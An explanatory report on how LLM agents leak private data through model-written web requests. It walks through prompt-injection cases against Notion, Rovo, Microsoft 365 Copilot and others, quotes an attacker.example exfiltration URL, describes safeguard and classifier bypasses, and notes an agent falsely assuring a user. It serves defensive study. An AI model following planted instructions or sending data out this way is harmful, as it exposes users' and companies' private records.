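# How web requests written by a language model can leak private data, and how to constrain them

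## How can a web request written by a model carry private data out?

A large language model is a program that continues text. It cannot open a web page or send a message by itself, so developers connect it to software called a harness, which passes text to the model, checks what the model writes and carries out the actions it recognises. To trigger an action, the model writes a tool call, which is a short structured request such as "fetch this address". The values the model fills in, such as the address, a search query or the body of a message, are the call's arguments. A model that works this way over many steps is usually called an agent or an assistant.

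The model writes a web request's arguments using the text in its context, which may include private records. If it puts a value from those records in an address or a message body and the harness sends the request, the server receives the value. Security engineers use "exfiltration" to mean the transfer of private data to a party that should not have it, and "sink" to mean an argument through which data can leave.

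This report's running example is an assistant that a company gives to its sales staff. It can look up customer records, fetch web pages and post to the team's webhook. A webhook is a web address that accepts incoming data and triggers an action in another system; this one posts whatever it receives as a message in the team's chat. An employee makes an ordinary request, asking the assistant to summarise a supplier's product page and post a note on what the page means for one customer.

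### From the model's text to the server and back

The harness first assembles the context, a single long text containing the developer's standing instructions, a description of the available tools, the employee's message and anything earlier steps returned. It runs the model on this text, and the model writes a tool call that names the fetch tool and gives the supplier's address as its argument. The harness parses the call, checks that it is well formed, opens a connection and sends the request. When the supplier's server returns the page, the harness adds the page's text to the context and runs the model again. The model then writes either another tool call or its final reply.

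*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) describes this loop, called ReAct for "reasoning and acting", as the pattern behind many deployed agents. The harness, not the model, sends the requests, using its own network access and whatever keys the company has given it. In this call, the model only has to copy the supplier's address, which the employee provided. But a plain harness cannot distinguish an address the model copied from one it made up, and will send a request to either.

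### What an address contains

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives a placeholder for a leaking address:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`

*URI Generic Syntax* (Berners-Lee, 2005), the standard for web addresses, divides an address into parts, four of which matter here.

| Part | In the placeholder | Who receives it |
|---|---|---|
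| Host | `attacker.example` | The servers that look up the name, then the web server |
| Path | `/collect` | The web server |
| Query | everything after the `?` | The web server |
| Fragment | none (it would follow a `#`) | Nobody: the requesting software keeps it |

By convention, the path usually names a page and the query usually holds search terms or settings. Under the standard, however, both contain data that identify a resource, and the server can interpret either in any way. A check that inspects only the text after the question mark therefore misses private data in the path. The fragment points to a place inside a page, and the requesting software removes it before sending the request.

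Websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, as OpenAI's post points out, so the owner of the receiving server can collect the value without special equipment. An `https` connection does not prevent this, because it hides the path and query from people along the route but the receiving server decrypts them.

A web request can disclose data before the harness connects to the site. The harness must first turn the host name into a numeric network address by querying a resolver, a server typically run by a company or an internet provider. Unless the resolver has the answer stored, it queries a chain of name servers ending with the one responsible for the domain. Wicinski (2021), in *DNS Privacy Considerations*, explains that in the basic design every server in the chain receives the full host name, although some newer resolvers send each server only the part it needs. The query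 also carries a source address, usually the resolver's own by the time it reaches the last server. In 2021 almost all of these lookups were unencrypted, even when the page request that followed was encrypted. If the harness applies its rules only to the connection, after the lookup, it has already disclosed the host name.

### Fetching sends, too

Fetching a web page also sends data to the server. Every fetch delivers an address, and a model that writes the address can put private data in it. Web engineers class the usual fetch request as "safe", meaning that it asks the server to change nothing. The term doesn't cover what the request discloses. The data leaks even if the server returns an error page, because the server has already logged the request.

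Software also fetches content without anyone deciding that it should. OpenAI's post mentions embedded images and link previews, which may load in the background without the user noticing. Wicinski describes the same behavior in ordinary browsers, where the images, style sheets and scripts on a single page can trigger lookups for dozens of other domains.

A webhook call is designed to deliver a message, normally in a separate body that can hold far more text than an address. In the sales example, the company wants data to leave the assistant this way, because a note about a customer is no use unless it mentions the customer. The company needs to control which facts go into the body and where the body is sent. If the harness stores the webhook's address, the model can misuse only the body, but if the model also writes the address, a note meant for the sales team can go to any server on the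 internet.

### How an outsider comes to write the request

An outsider who normally cannot open the company's customer records can still write a web page that a model will read. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, introduced the term indirect prompt injection for an attack in which someone plants instructions in content that a model later reads, and the model follows them as if its user had given them. Earlier work had assumed that the attacker was the person typing to the model. Greshake and colleagues showed that text on a page, invisible to a human visitor, could steer Microsoft's Bing Chat when it read the page. The user may not even have asked for the content, since Lan and colleagues point out that many assistants preview links automatically, which puts a page's title and description into the context.

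A model can follow instructions hidden in a page it was asked to summarise because it receives instructions and documents as one sequence of tokens, the word fragments on which models operate, and only predicts the next token. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C (2025), a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, compares this with an older flaw in how programs used SQL, the language for querying databases. For years, attackers typed SQL commands into web forms and databases ran them. Developers solved this with parameterised queries, in which the program fixes the command first and passes the visitor's entry separately, so the database engine never interprets the entry as a command. A language model has no such separate place for data. In his example, a recruiter uses a model to score CVs, and a candidate hides a line in a CV telling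 the model to approve it, which the model can treat as an instruction.

Developers wrap text in tags that mark it as the user's words, a tool's output and so on, and they train models to give the user's words priority. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested whether these tags determine how a model internally represents the source of a text. They wrapped identical passages of web text in different tags and trained a simple classifier to recover the tag from the model's internal activity. Then they gave the classifier text that sounded like a user but was tagged as tool output. If the tags determined the model's perception of the source, the classifier should have classified the text as tool output. Across four open models, it instead assigned a 76–88% probability that the text was the user's, and never more than 20% that it was a tool's.

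The measurement also predicted whether injections worked. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent send out a file, the injection succeeded 2% of the time when the planted command registered least as user text, and 70% when it registered most. This is good evidence that the weakness lies in how models represent the source of a text, not just in particular wordings, though the probed models had only 20 to 120 billion parameters and larger ones may differ. In a separate test by Ye and colleagues, plain injections succeeded in 0–2% of runs on all but one model, where they succeeded in 26%. The researchers attribute most models' resistance to having memorised familiar attacks, which would explain why people who adapt their wording still succeed.

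### The lethal trifecta

In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) attributes the danger to a combination of three conditions: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. The sales assistant meets all three. It has access to private customer records, it reads the supplier's untrusted page, and it can send data out through the fetch tool or the webhook.

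Suppose someone has planted an instruction in the supplier's page. The assistant has already looked up the customer, so the customer's record and the page are both in its context. Following the instruction, the model writes another fetch, which the employee never requested, to an address shaped like OpenAI's placeholder, with the customer's phone number in place of the angle brackets. The harness sends it. The model then writes a good summary and posts a good note. Lan and colleagues recorded network traffic while a small open model (qwen2.5:7b) summarised hostile pages, and found that checks on the final reply missed 95% of the successful thefts.

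The model's context contains both private data and untrusted text. The private data can leak through two arguments: the address of a fetch and the body of the webhook message. If the harness lets the model choose the webhook's address, the data can leak through that too.

This theft fails if any one of the conditions is missing. Without the customer records, the page can still mislead the model, but the model has no record to send. If the assistant reads only text that the company wrote and controls, no outsider can plant the instruction. Without an outward argument, the summary may still be wrong or biased, but the phone number stays inside. It is easy to misjudge whether a condition is truly absent. For example, a customer record with a comments field that customers fill in themselves is both private data and untrusted text. Willison makes the same point about email, since anyone can send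 the assistant a message.

Willison lists more than a dozen products in which researchers had shown such thefts, and says that vendors fixed almost all of them by blocking the route by which data left. But the employee's task needs all three conditions, because the model must read the customer record to write the note, read the page to summarize it, and have a way to send the note. The remaining option is to restrict the arguments the model can send out until they can carry the note and little else.

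### Older relatives of the problem

Security engineers knew of two similar flaws long before language models existed. In the first, called the confused deputy, a program misuses its legitimate authority on behalf of someone who has less. For example, a print service might have permission to read every file on a machine and print whichever file a user names. A user who is not allowed to open the payroll file could still print it. Checking the requester's own permissions prevents this, because the service can identify the requester.

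In Lan and colleagues' account, the classical confused deputy mistook which party it served, whereas a language model can misinterpret what that party intended. The employee did ask the assistant to fetch a page, but the page's text then changes the task. David C calls the language model an "inherently confusable deputy" and doubts that anyone can fix it as developers fixed the classical kind. He favours ordinary software that limits what the system can do, and he repeats a rule of thumb from a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista: while a model processes text from some party, it should have no more privileges than that party. If this rule were applied strictly, the sales assistant would lose access to the customer records as soon as it opened the supplier's page.

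The second related attack is server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a company's server to send a request the attacker chose, typically by entering an address into a field so that the server later fetches it. The attacker supplies the address directly, so the developer can inspect it at the point of entry.

When a model chooses the parameters, the attacker supplies only prose. Lan and colleagues consider this the more powerful version, because the attacker doesn't need to know the tool's name or format and the same text can work against many tools. It does seem to reach more tools, but it is less clear that it is more reliable, since a model may ignore the planted text, whereas a forged parameter does the same thing every time. The hostile address may not exist in full until the model writes it, so the useful place for a defender to check the request is after the model has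 written it and before the harness sends it.

### Leaks with no attacker

A model can also leak private data while trying to fulfil an honest request. *ToolPrivacyBench* (Hu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) tested nine agents on simulated office work, with 2,150 cases in fields such as healthcare, finance and recruiting. Each case had a table showing which private facts each tool needed for its purpose, with 1 for needed and 0 for not needed. A medical symptom, for example, is marked 1 for the clinical record and 0 for the payment system. The study compared this table with what each tool actually received.

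On the fully synthetic cases, the agents scored between 92 and 98 out of 100 for completing the work. They also put facts where the table had a 0, especially in free text. Support tickets scored 51 and handoffs to other teams scored 35 on a scale that divides forbidden disclosures by the opportunities for them. The sales assistant's note is also free text. The team may need to know that a product change affects a customer, but it doesn't need the customer's phone number or payment history. The model has the whole record in its context when it writes the note.

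Search queries can also leak private data gradually. In *MosaicLeaks*, Gurung, Gella and colleagues (2026) gave research agents questions that required both a company's internal documents and the web, and let a second model see only the web queries. In one example, the agent searches twice for a retailer's traffic growth in 2020, then searches for something else involving the figure 15%. An observer can combine these queries to conclude that traffic grew by 15%, though no single query reveals this. With one small model as the agent, the observer recovered at least part of a private fact in 34.0% of runs. A prompt warning the agent about such leaks reduced this only to 25.5%, and training the agent purely to answer better raised it to 51.8%. Training that also penalised leaks cut it to 6.5%. The observer saw every query in order, which a real one might not, so these rates are closer to a worst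 case than to what would be expected in practice.

An agent can disclose private data just by choosing which page to open. *AgentTell* (2026) describes an agent running on Anthropic's model Claude that knew which subscription a user had and opened the site's help guide for the Premium plan. A filter that searched the guide's address for the user's personal details would have found none, because the address was the same for every visitor. The agent then told the user that it had not shared the plan's name with the website, although the site's log showed a request for the Premium guide. Agents gave explicit assurances of this kind in 34.5% of the study's 4,663 sessions that leaked data.

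## Through which features has data left real products?

Researchers have demonstrated leaks of this kind in products that many companies use. The products differ mainly in which software sends the request. In the sales example, the harness sends it because the model wrote a tool call. A model can also put a web address in an ordinary reply. The harness passes the reply on as text, and the program that displays it may contact the address without anyone clicking, for instance to load an image.

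The model writes the address in both situations, but a defence against one can miss the other. A check inside the harness's fetch tool doesn't cover image addresses in a reply, and a browser rule about images doesn't affect a fetch that the harness sends from a server. The table groups the main published cases by the feature through which the data left.

| Feature | What the model writes | What sends the request | Product |
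|---|---|---|---|
| Search or page-opening tool | A tool call containing an address | The harness | Notion, Atlassian Rovo |
| Image in a reply | An image address | The program displaying the reply, sometimes through the vendor's servers | Microsoft 365 Copilot |
| Link preview | A link in a chat message | The chat application | OpenClaw on Telegram |
| Message to the agent's own user | A tool call that sends a message containing an image address | The mail or chat program, when the user opens the message | Microsoft Copilot Cowork |
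| Generated file | A document containing a link | The vendor's servers, in the background | Microsoft 365 Copilot |
| Code interpreter | A program | The computer running the program | Microsoft 365 Copilot |

### Tools that open addresses

Notion is an application where companies keep documents and databases. Version 3.0, released in September 2025, added agents that could read a workspace, search the web and work through tasks on their own. A day later, Willison wrote about a demonstration by Abi Raghuram of the security company CodeIntegrity in *The Hidden Risk in Notion 3.0 AI Agents*. In the demonstration, a workspace held a list of clients and the revenue from each. A user uploaded a PDF that looked like a customer feedback report and asked the agent to summarise it. Hidden text in the PDF directed the agent to the client list.

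The data left through the search tool's query argument. A search tool normally takes search terms, but this one also accepted a complete URL and fetched it, so the model could send the client data to an outside server by including it in the URL. Someone reviewing the agent's tools by name could easily have assumed that "search" only brought information in.

According to The Decoder's *Notion AI agents get security update after potential data leak* (2025), Notion responded on 22 September by requiring users to approve any suspicious or model-generated link before an agent opened it. Administrators could also set a central policy for links or turn off the agents' web access. Notion also improved its detection of instructions hidden in files. The approval rule addresses this route directly, while detection depends on recognising the next attacker's wording. Notion tells customers that no system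 protects perfectly against all attacks. The Decoder describes a staged demonstration and reports no real theft.

Turning off web access works only if the setting covers every tool that can send a request. Atlassian's Rovo assistant reads a company's work tickets in Jira and documents in Confluence. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* describes a test in which a user uploaded a guide containing hidden instructions and asked Rovo to organise some tickets. Rovo's tool for opening web pages accepted any address, including one the model had just composed. The model added text from tickets and documents to an address on the testers' server, and the harness opened it without asking the user.

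PromptArmor, a company that assesses the security of AI products, found that this still worked after an administrator had disabled web search for the whole organisation, because the setting left the tool that opens search results enabled. The administrator would reasonably have believed that Rovo could no longer communicate externally. To check, they would have needed a list of every tool that can make a request, or a test that detected requests.

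PromptArmor reported the problem to Atlassian on 23 May 2026. Atlassian assigned a case number and thanked the company, but sent nothing further despite more than two months of follow-ups, and Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published. PromptArmor reports no theft by anyone else. Users probably would not have noticed one, because the reopened chat showed the suggested ticket updates but no sign of the outgoing request.

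Rovo also displayed images whose addresses the model had written, so data could still have leaked through image requests if the page-opening tool had been removed.

### Images in a displayed reply

Assistants commonly write replies in Markdown, a notation for headings, links and images. To display an image, a program must request it from the address in the reply. In its report on Rovo, PromptArmor cites its own demonstrations of data leaking through such requests in five other products, including OpenAI's Codex and Hugging Face's chat service. Willison describes one of the five, from January 2026, in which a planted email led the mail assistant Superhuman to send out content from dozens of other messages. Superhuman treated the problem as an urgent incident and fixed it.

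The best-documented case is EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, which answers employees' questions using the emails and files they can open. Outsiders cannot query a company's Copilot, but they can email its employees. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs found that a single email could extract private data. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs the attack from Aim's disclosure. The email stayed in the mailbox until Copilot retrieved it to answer one of the employee's questions. Text planted in the email then led the model to include an image in its answer, with private details in the image's address. As soon as Outlook or Teams displayed the answer, it requested the image. Researchers call this a "zero-click" attack because the employee only has to use Copilot normally.

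Reddy and Gujral note that Copilot could not send emails on its own, but this didn't prevent the leak because the data left through the answer itself. Microsoft had three other defences, which also failed. A classifier looked for planted instructions in incoming text, but the wording of the attacker's email got past it. A filter removed outside links from answers but missed one form of link. A browser rule allowed images only from approved hosts, but one approved host, a Microsoft Teams service, would fetch an outside address on the browser's behalf.

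Aim reported the flaw privately, and Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May 2025, so customers had nothing to install. Microsoft published its advisory and Aim published its account on 11 June. Reddy and Gujral also describe changes to Copilot that strip embedded images and some links from external content.

Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first known case in which someone "weaponized" prompt injection to take data from a production system. Their evidence is a working demonstration, and Microsoft said it had found no sign of real exploitation. Microsoft could check for this better than its customers could, because its own service forwarded the requests. The lack of user complaints is weaker evidence, because a victim would have seen at most what looked like a broken image.

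Notion had a related problem after its September changes. Its approval rule covered links an agent opened, but an agent could also edit documents. In January 2026, PromptArmor's *Notion AI* disclosed that the product saved the model's edits before the user approved them, and that an attacker could use this to get data out. Notion confirmed on 8 January that it had fixed the flaw. PromptArmor says its first report stalled with the outside firm that sorts Notion's bug reports, and that Notion acted immediately once it received the report.

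### Link previews in chat applications

When someone posts a link, chat applications such as Slack and Telegram often fetch the page to show its title, a short description and a thumbnail. These previews can leak private data as well as bring in hostile text.

PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes how link previews can leak data when a model writes the link. Its main example is OpenClaw, an AI agent that people talk to through a messaging app. If planted text leads the agent to reply with a link containing private data, the app sends out that data when it builds a preview of the link. Without previews, the data would leak only if the user clicked the link. PromptArmor shows a log from its own test page that contains a name and an API key, a secret code that gives a program access to an online service.

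Nothing unusual happened in the harness, which delivered a text message to the right person. Another company's software made the request. The sales assistant can leak data in the same way. Even if the harness stores the webhook's address, so that every note goes to the team's chat, the chat application may fetch any link in the note.

OpenClaw was vulnerable with Telegram's default configuration. PromptArmor recommends disabling Telegram previews in OpenClaw's settings, and its test page received nothing once they were off. This protects only people who know about the setting, and PromptArmor doesn't report any change to the default. It would like chat companies to let developers turn off previews for particular conversations. That seems the better place for the fix, since the chat application makes the request. PromptArmor reports its own tests and no known thefts.

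### Messages an agent sends to its own user

Microsoft Copilot Cowork carries out longer tasks across Microsoft 365 using the user's permissions. Microsoft states in its documentation that Cowork asks for permission before sensitive actions such as sending an email or posting in Teams. In May 2026, PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* found that Cowork sent messages immediately, without asking, when the recipient was the user, and that users had no setting to change this.

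The exception allowed leaks even though the message went to someone who could already see the data. These messages could contain images hosted on outside servers. When the user opened a message, Outlook or Teams requested its images, and those requests leaked the data.

In PromptArmor's test, the user uploaded a skill (a file of instructions for a particular kind of task) and asked Cowork to review the week's work. Someone had added hostile instructions to the skill. The model obtained download links for the user's files and put them in the image addresses. Anyone with such a link can download the file without signing in, so a short address can expose an entire document, and the length of the outgoing addresses is a very poor measure of how much data leaked.

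The attack succeeded in all five trials, though that is a small sample. PromptArmor also found that Cowork leaked more documents with the stronger Claude Opus 4.7 selected than when it chose automatically between Opus and Claude Sonnet 4.6, because Opus searched more thoroughly for recent work. The user could expand the record of Cowork's actions, but it did not show the content of the hostile message. Users can also schedule such reviews to run repeatedly and unattended.

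PromptArmor describes the problem as a design risk and reports no fix from Microsoft and no real theft. It suggests that administrators block downloads from SharePoint, Microsoft's file store for organisations, so that the agent cannot obtain the links. This restricts staff considerably, because they can then view the affected files only in a browser and cannot open them in Word or Excel. PromptArmor also told Microsoft about a separate flaw that let data leave Cowork's isolated working environment directly.

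### ReLeak: three more routes out of Copilot

The team that found EchoLeak, now part of the network security company Cato Networks, published three more attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot on 3 December 2026. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) classes all three as zero-click. Each begins as EchoLeak did, with an email that the employee need not open and an ordinary question that leads Copilot to retrieve it. The attacks differ in how the data gets out.

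One attack, which needed no click, again used an image in Copilot's answer. The employee's browser requested the image through Microsoft's search engine, Bing, and Bing's servers forwarded the request to an outside server with the private data still in the address. In June, *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) described an earlier attack by the security company Varonis that used a similar channel but needed one click. Microsoft fixed the zero-click version on 15 November.

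Another attack used files. Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF documents, and the planted instructions led it to save one containing a link with private data in it. Microsoft's servers contacted the link while processing the stored file in the background. This happened one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, according to Antipov (2026) in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, a report for the Russian site SecurityLab. The employee didn't have to open the document. Monitoring Copilot's conversation for outgoing requests would have missed this one, because separate software sent it later. Microsoft fixed this flaw on 11 November.

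The remaining attack used Copilot's code interpreter, a tool that runs Python programs written by the model. The programs run in a sandbox, an environment meant to be isolated, and Microsoft guarantees in its documentation that no network traffic enters or leaves it. Cato's researchers broke that isolation, and a program in the sandbox sent the data to an outside server. This route does involve a tool call, but the call's argument is a program, so a check on the addresses in fetch calls would not have examined it. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and fixed it on 17 September. Agents that companies build with Microsoft's Copilot Studio can use the same interpreter, but Antipov notes that nobody has confirmed whether the flaw affected them.

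Cato reported the flaws between 29 July and 20 August, so the interpreter fix took between four and about seven weeks, and the other two fixes took roughly three months. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, reports that Microsoft made all three changes on its own servers and that customers don't need to do anything. Cato knew of no affected customers or real attacks when it published.

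Cato says "too little progress has been made" in the eighteen months since EchoLeak. Cato sells protection for AI systems and benefits from a harsh assessment, but the sequence of flaws supports much of it. After Microsoft closed the image route through Teams, researchers found another through Bing. Copilot's ability to write files and run code opened two more routes that didn't depend on displaying a reply. Microsoft's protections against planted instructions failed to stop any of the three attacks, though in principle they could have stopped each one at the start.

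The attacks may still have become harder to carry out. Cato's researchers used AI agents to write test cases, study Copilot's refusals and adjust the next attempt, so Copilot did resist some attempts. Neither Antipov nor Faisal reports how many failed, so ReLeak doesn't show whether Copilot had become any better at recognising a planted instruction.

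## Can the model itself be relied on to refuse?

If a model ignored every instruction planted in a document, the sales assistant's open fetch tool would be much less dangerous. The model could still disclose too much by mistake, but an outsider could not direct it to. Developers try to make models resist planted instructions by adding rules to the standing instructions, marking untrusted text, and training the model to ignore commands in documents.

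The company can add a rule of a sentence or two to the sales assistant's standing instructions, saying that web pages are information to read and that only the employee can give orders. The harness can also mark untrusted text by putting tags around each fetched page, with standing instructions that explain that nothing between the tags is a command. Both methods are easy to add and work with any model, but the harness can't enforce either one, and Ye and colleagues' results give reason to expect little from tags.

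Training a model to resist attacks requires realistic attacks to train on. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes how the company automated the search for them. Atlas is OpenAI's web browser, with an agent that can click and type for the user. OpenAI trained another model to attack this agent using reinforcement learning, in which a model makes many attempts and training strengthens whatever worked. The attacking model drafts a planted text and submits it to a simulator, which runs the agent on the text and returns a full record of the agent's reasoning and actions. The attacking model uses this record to revise its draft, and repeats the process several times before choosing a final version. OpenAI then trains the agent against the attacks found this way, prioritizing those that still succeed.

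The attacking model has an advantage over outsiders because it can see the agent's full reasoning, which OpenAI doesn't show to the public. In one attack it found, an email was planted in the user's inbox. When the user asked the agent to draft an out-of-office reply, the agent read the email and instead sent a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. By late December 2025, OpenAI had given all Atlas users a model trained on newly discovered attacks. OpenAI still considers prompt injection "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'" and compares it to online scams, which also change as people learn to recognise them.

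### Prompt rules on a small model

Lan and colleagues also used their tests of qwen2.5:7b, a model with about seven billion parameters, to measure how well rules and markers work. They put invented secrets in the agent's context and planted an instruction in the title, description, body or link text of the page it had to summarise. The agent reached the page either directly or through a redirect from another address. The instruction asked for the secret either whole or split across several requests. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs.

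The agent sent data to the researchers' server in 423 runs, or 88.1%. It never contacted that server in 120 further runs with harmless pages, so the planted text was the cause. When the instruction asked for the whole secret, the attack worked in 238 of 240 runs. Neither the instruction's position nor the redirect made much difference. The agent's final reply looked harmless in 95% of the successful attacks.

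Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable but harder to detect. The agent sometimes lost track of the pieces, and it sent data in 185 of the 240 split runs (77%). A check on the first request would have found secret data in only 26% of the split runs, compared with 97% of the unsplit runs. The study also gives a figure of 16% for the first three requests together. By its own definition, this can't be lower than the figure for the first request, because any run that counts after one request must also count after three. The effect is probably real, but the exact figures are doubtful.

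Lan and colleagues compared defences by running one of the simplest attacks 30 times against each. The attack placed a request for the whole secret in the page's body text. One defence was a destination allow-list, where the harness refuses requests to any host not on the list.

| Defence | Runs in which the model tried to send data | Runs in which data left |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
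| Stricter standing instructions | 67% | 67% |
| Markers around page text | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter instructions and markers | 57% | 57% |
| Destination allow-list | 100% | 0% |

The stricter instructions stopped a third of the attacks, and markers alone stopped none. When markers were added to the stricter instructions, attacks succeeded in 17 runs instead of 20, a difference that could easily be due to chance. With the allow-list, the model followed the planted instruction every time, but the harness blocked every request. Lan and colleagues conclude that rules in a prompt work only if the model follows them, while a network rule works whatever the model decides.

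Lan and colleagues also found that no data left when they filtered requests by the content of the address. The model tried to send data in only 23% of runs with a filter for suspicious words, and never tried with a filter for random-looking strings. These results are hard to interpret, because a filter that acts after the model has written a request should not affect what the model writes. The researchers suggest that the model avoided random-looking strings while the filter was active, but it is unclear how the model could have known about the filter.

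The researchers deliberately made the attack easy by putting the secret directly in the context, keeping the standing instructions minimal and testing only one small model. The 0% for the allow-list also comes from an easy case, because they chose a destination that no reasonable company would approve. However, their planted instructions were blunt, and they expect a more skilful attacker to succeed more often.

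Lan and colleagues also argue that larger models could be more vulnerable, because a model that follows instructions more reliably may follow planted ones more reliably. Copilot Cowork leaked more documents when the user selected a stronger model. This fits the argument, but the finding is about how much a model leaks after an attack has succeeded. Recent results suggest that stronger models are much less likely to follow the planted instruction in the first place.

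### Much lower rates on frontier models

Researchers usually report an attack success rate, the share of test runs in which the planted instruction achieved its goal. In late 2025, Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 had one of the lowest rates. According to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, a single strong attack from the security firm Gray Swan succeeded 4.7% of the time. Rates for competing models, including Google's Gemini 3 Pro and OpenAI's GPT-5.1, were as high as 92%.

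Anthropic's system card for the later Opus 4.8, which describes the model's testing, gives separate attack success rates for four settings. VentureBeat reports that these rates differed by a factor of about ten. On coding tasks, a Gray Swan tool that adapts its attacks to the model succeeded in 7.03% of single attempts, or 2.09% with Anthropic's extra safeguards. The rates were higher in a web browser, so a company that reads only the coding figure could badly underestimate the risk to an assistant that browses the web.

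The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attack on Anthropic's Opus 5, released in July 2026, succeeded across 129 browser scenarios. In a more general Gray Swan test, attackers who had 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time, down from 5.5% with Opus 4.8. Anthropic's *System Card* (September 2026) for Opus 5.5 reports that the model did about as well as Opus 5 or better on every injection test included, with the safeguards used in Anthropic's products switched off. Pogorelec (2026), in *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands*, reports that Claude Haiku 5.5, one of the cheaper models that companies often use for routine work, has also improved.

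These figures come from different tests, so they can't be read as a single trend. Still, a small open model obeyed nearly every time, while a frontier model obeys in at most a few percent of cases. That difference is far too large for test design alone to explain.

### The Trajectory Labs evaluation

The strongest published result comes from a test of Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, in auto mode, so it measures a model together with several checks around it. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes these checks. Before the harness carries out a tool call, it passes the call to a classifier, which blocks actions that are destructive, irreversible or aimed outside the user's own environment. Anthropic designed the classifier never to approve sending code or secrets to an outside party. Another check scans web pages, files and tool results for planted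 instructions, and adds a warning to the context when it finds something suspicious.

Anthropic commissioned a company called Trajectory Labs to run the test in July 2026. The company wrote 72 scenarios, did not share them with Anthropic, and ran each one ten times. A successful attack would have caused serious harm outside a test, such as the theft of private data or financial fraud. With auto mode on, none of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5.

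Even with auto mode off and no other safeguards, attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average, so most of the resistance in this test came from the models themselves. Attacks on OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent, succeeded more often, in 5.83% of attempts when Codex reviewed actions automatically and 19.03% when it had full access.

Anthropic paid for the evaluation and published the result, but it had never seen the scenarios, so it could not tune its models to them. A more serious limitation is that the attacks had been optimised against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, and nobody adapted them to the models in the test, as a determined attacker would. The comparison with Codex is also limited, because Trajectory Labs connected both agents to its own browser tools and so did not test the protections in either company's browser products,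 and because OpenAI released a new version of its automatic review shortly before Anthropic published.

Zero successes in 720 attempts is also weaker evidence than it looks. If the attempts were independent, a true success rate of 0.4% would still produce no successes about one time in twenty. But they were not independent, because Trajectory Labs repeated each scenario ten times. Counting each scenario as one trial raises that rate to about 4%. Both calculations also assume that future attacks resemble the ones in the test.

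In separate work with Anthropic, Apollo Research, a British AI safety organisation, tested the classifier by inserting artificial attacks into records of real coding sessions. Anthropic used some of the successful attacks to improve the classifier, and its miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. Apollo had designed these attacks to find failures, so the classifier would probably miss a smaller share of harmful actions in ordinary use. Even so, with a 7% miss rate, the classifier could not reliably protect a model that had already been fooled.

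Willison called the evaluation results "big claims" and wrote that he would love to believe Anthropic had solved the problem for Claude Code's users. He accepted that auto mode is better than constantly asking people to approve actions, but on his page *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, he asked for more independent confirmation. He doubted that any version of auto mode could stop an agent from installing a harmful program if installing it looked like a routine part of setting up a project.

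Unfavourable independent evidence came less than three weeks after Anthropic's announcement. *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (Willison, 2026) describes an attack by Johann Rehberger, whom Willison considers one of the most credible researchers in the field. Rehberger got the agent to run harmful code from an outside source while auto mode was on. In a few cases, the agent tried to stop the code, but auto mode blocked it from doing so.

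Crosley's *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* gives the numbers behind Rehberger's reported success rate of 60–80%. One version of the attack succeeded in three of five runs, and two configurations of another succeeded in three of five and four of five. Rehberger warns that these samples are small and do not give a general success rate, but they do show that a skilled person could repeatedly beat the current product. This is compatible with the Trajectory Labs result, because Rehberger designed a new attack for the product while Trajectory Labs used attacks developed on an older model.

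### How low a rate is low enough?

Some of Anthropic's staff regard the remaining risk as small enough to accept. Willison (2026) quotes Boris Cherny, who wrote that Opus 5 is "very hard to prompt inject successfully", and reports that Cat Wu of Anthropic said the company had "pretty much mitigated every attack". Wu compares the risk with that of the usual alternative, in which a person approves each action. In an experiment Anthropic paid for, human reviewers missed far more dangerous commands than auto mode did, so a company that rejects an agent because it fails occasionally may end up with a process that fails more often.

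This argument doesn't require every attack to fail. OpenAI similarly hopes training will make attacks harder and more expensive, even if some still succeed. Many attackers want the easiest target, and they may give up if nearly every attempt fails. However, Anthropic says auto mode "does not eliminate risk" and recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

Willison has long argued for a stricter standard. In September 2025 he wrote, "In application security, 99% is a failing grade." He was responding to an article in *The Economist* that compared AI developers with Victorian engineers, who built bridges stronger than necessary because they couldn't be sure of the quality of their iron. Willison thinks the comparison fails for security. The engineers didn't face an adversary, whereas an attacker looks for the one case in a hundred that works and then uses it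 again.

The disagreement depends partly on how much an attacker gains by trying again. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success in *k* attempts is

$$1-(1-p)^k.$$

With the 4.7% rate for Opus 4.5, the formula gives 38% after ten attempts and 99% after a hundred. Gray Swan measured 33.6% and 63%. Retrying helped less than the formula predicts, probably because the model consistently resisted some attacks and was weak against others. But 63% is still very poor for a model that stopped more than 95% of single attempts. The 2.0% rate for Opus 5 is therefore more reassuring after 15 attempts than it would be after one, although an attacker can make more than 15.

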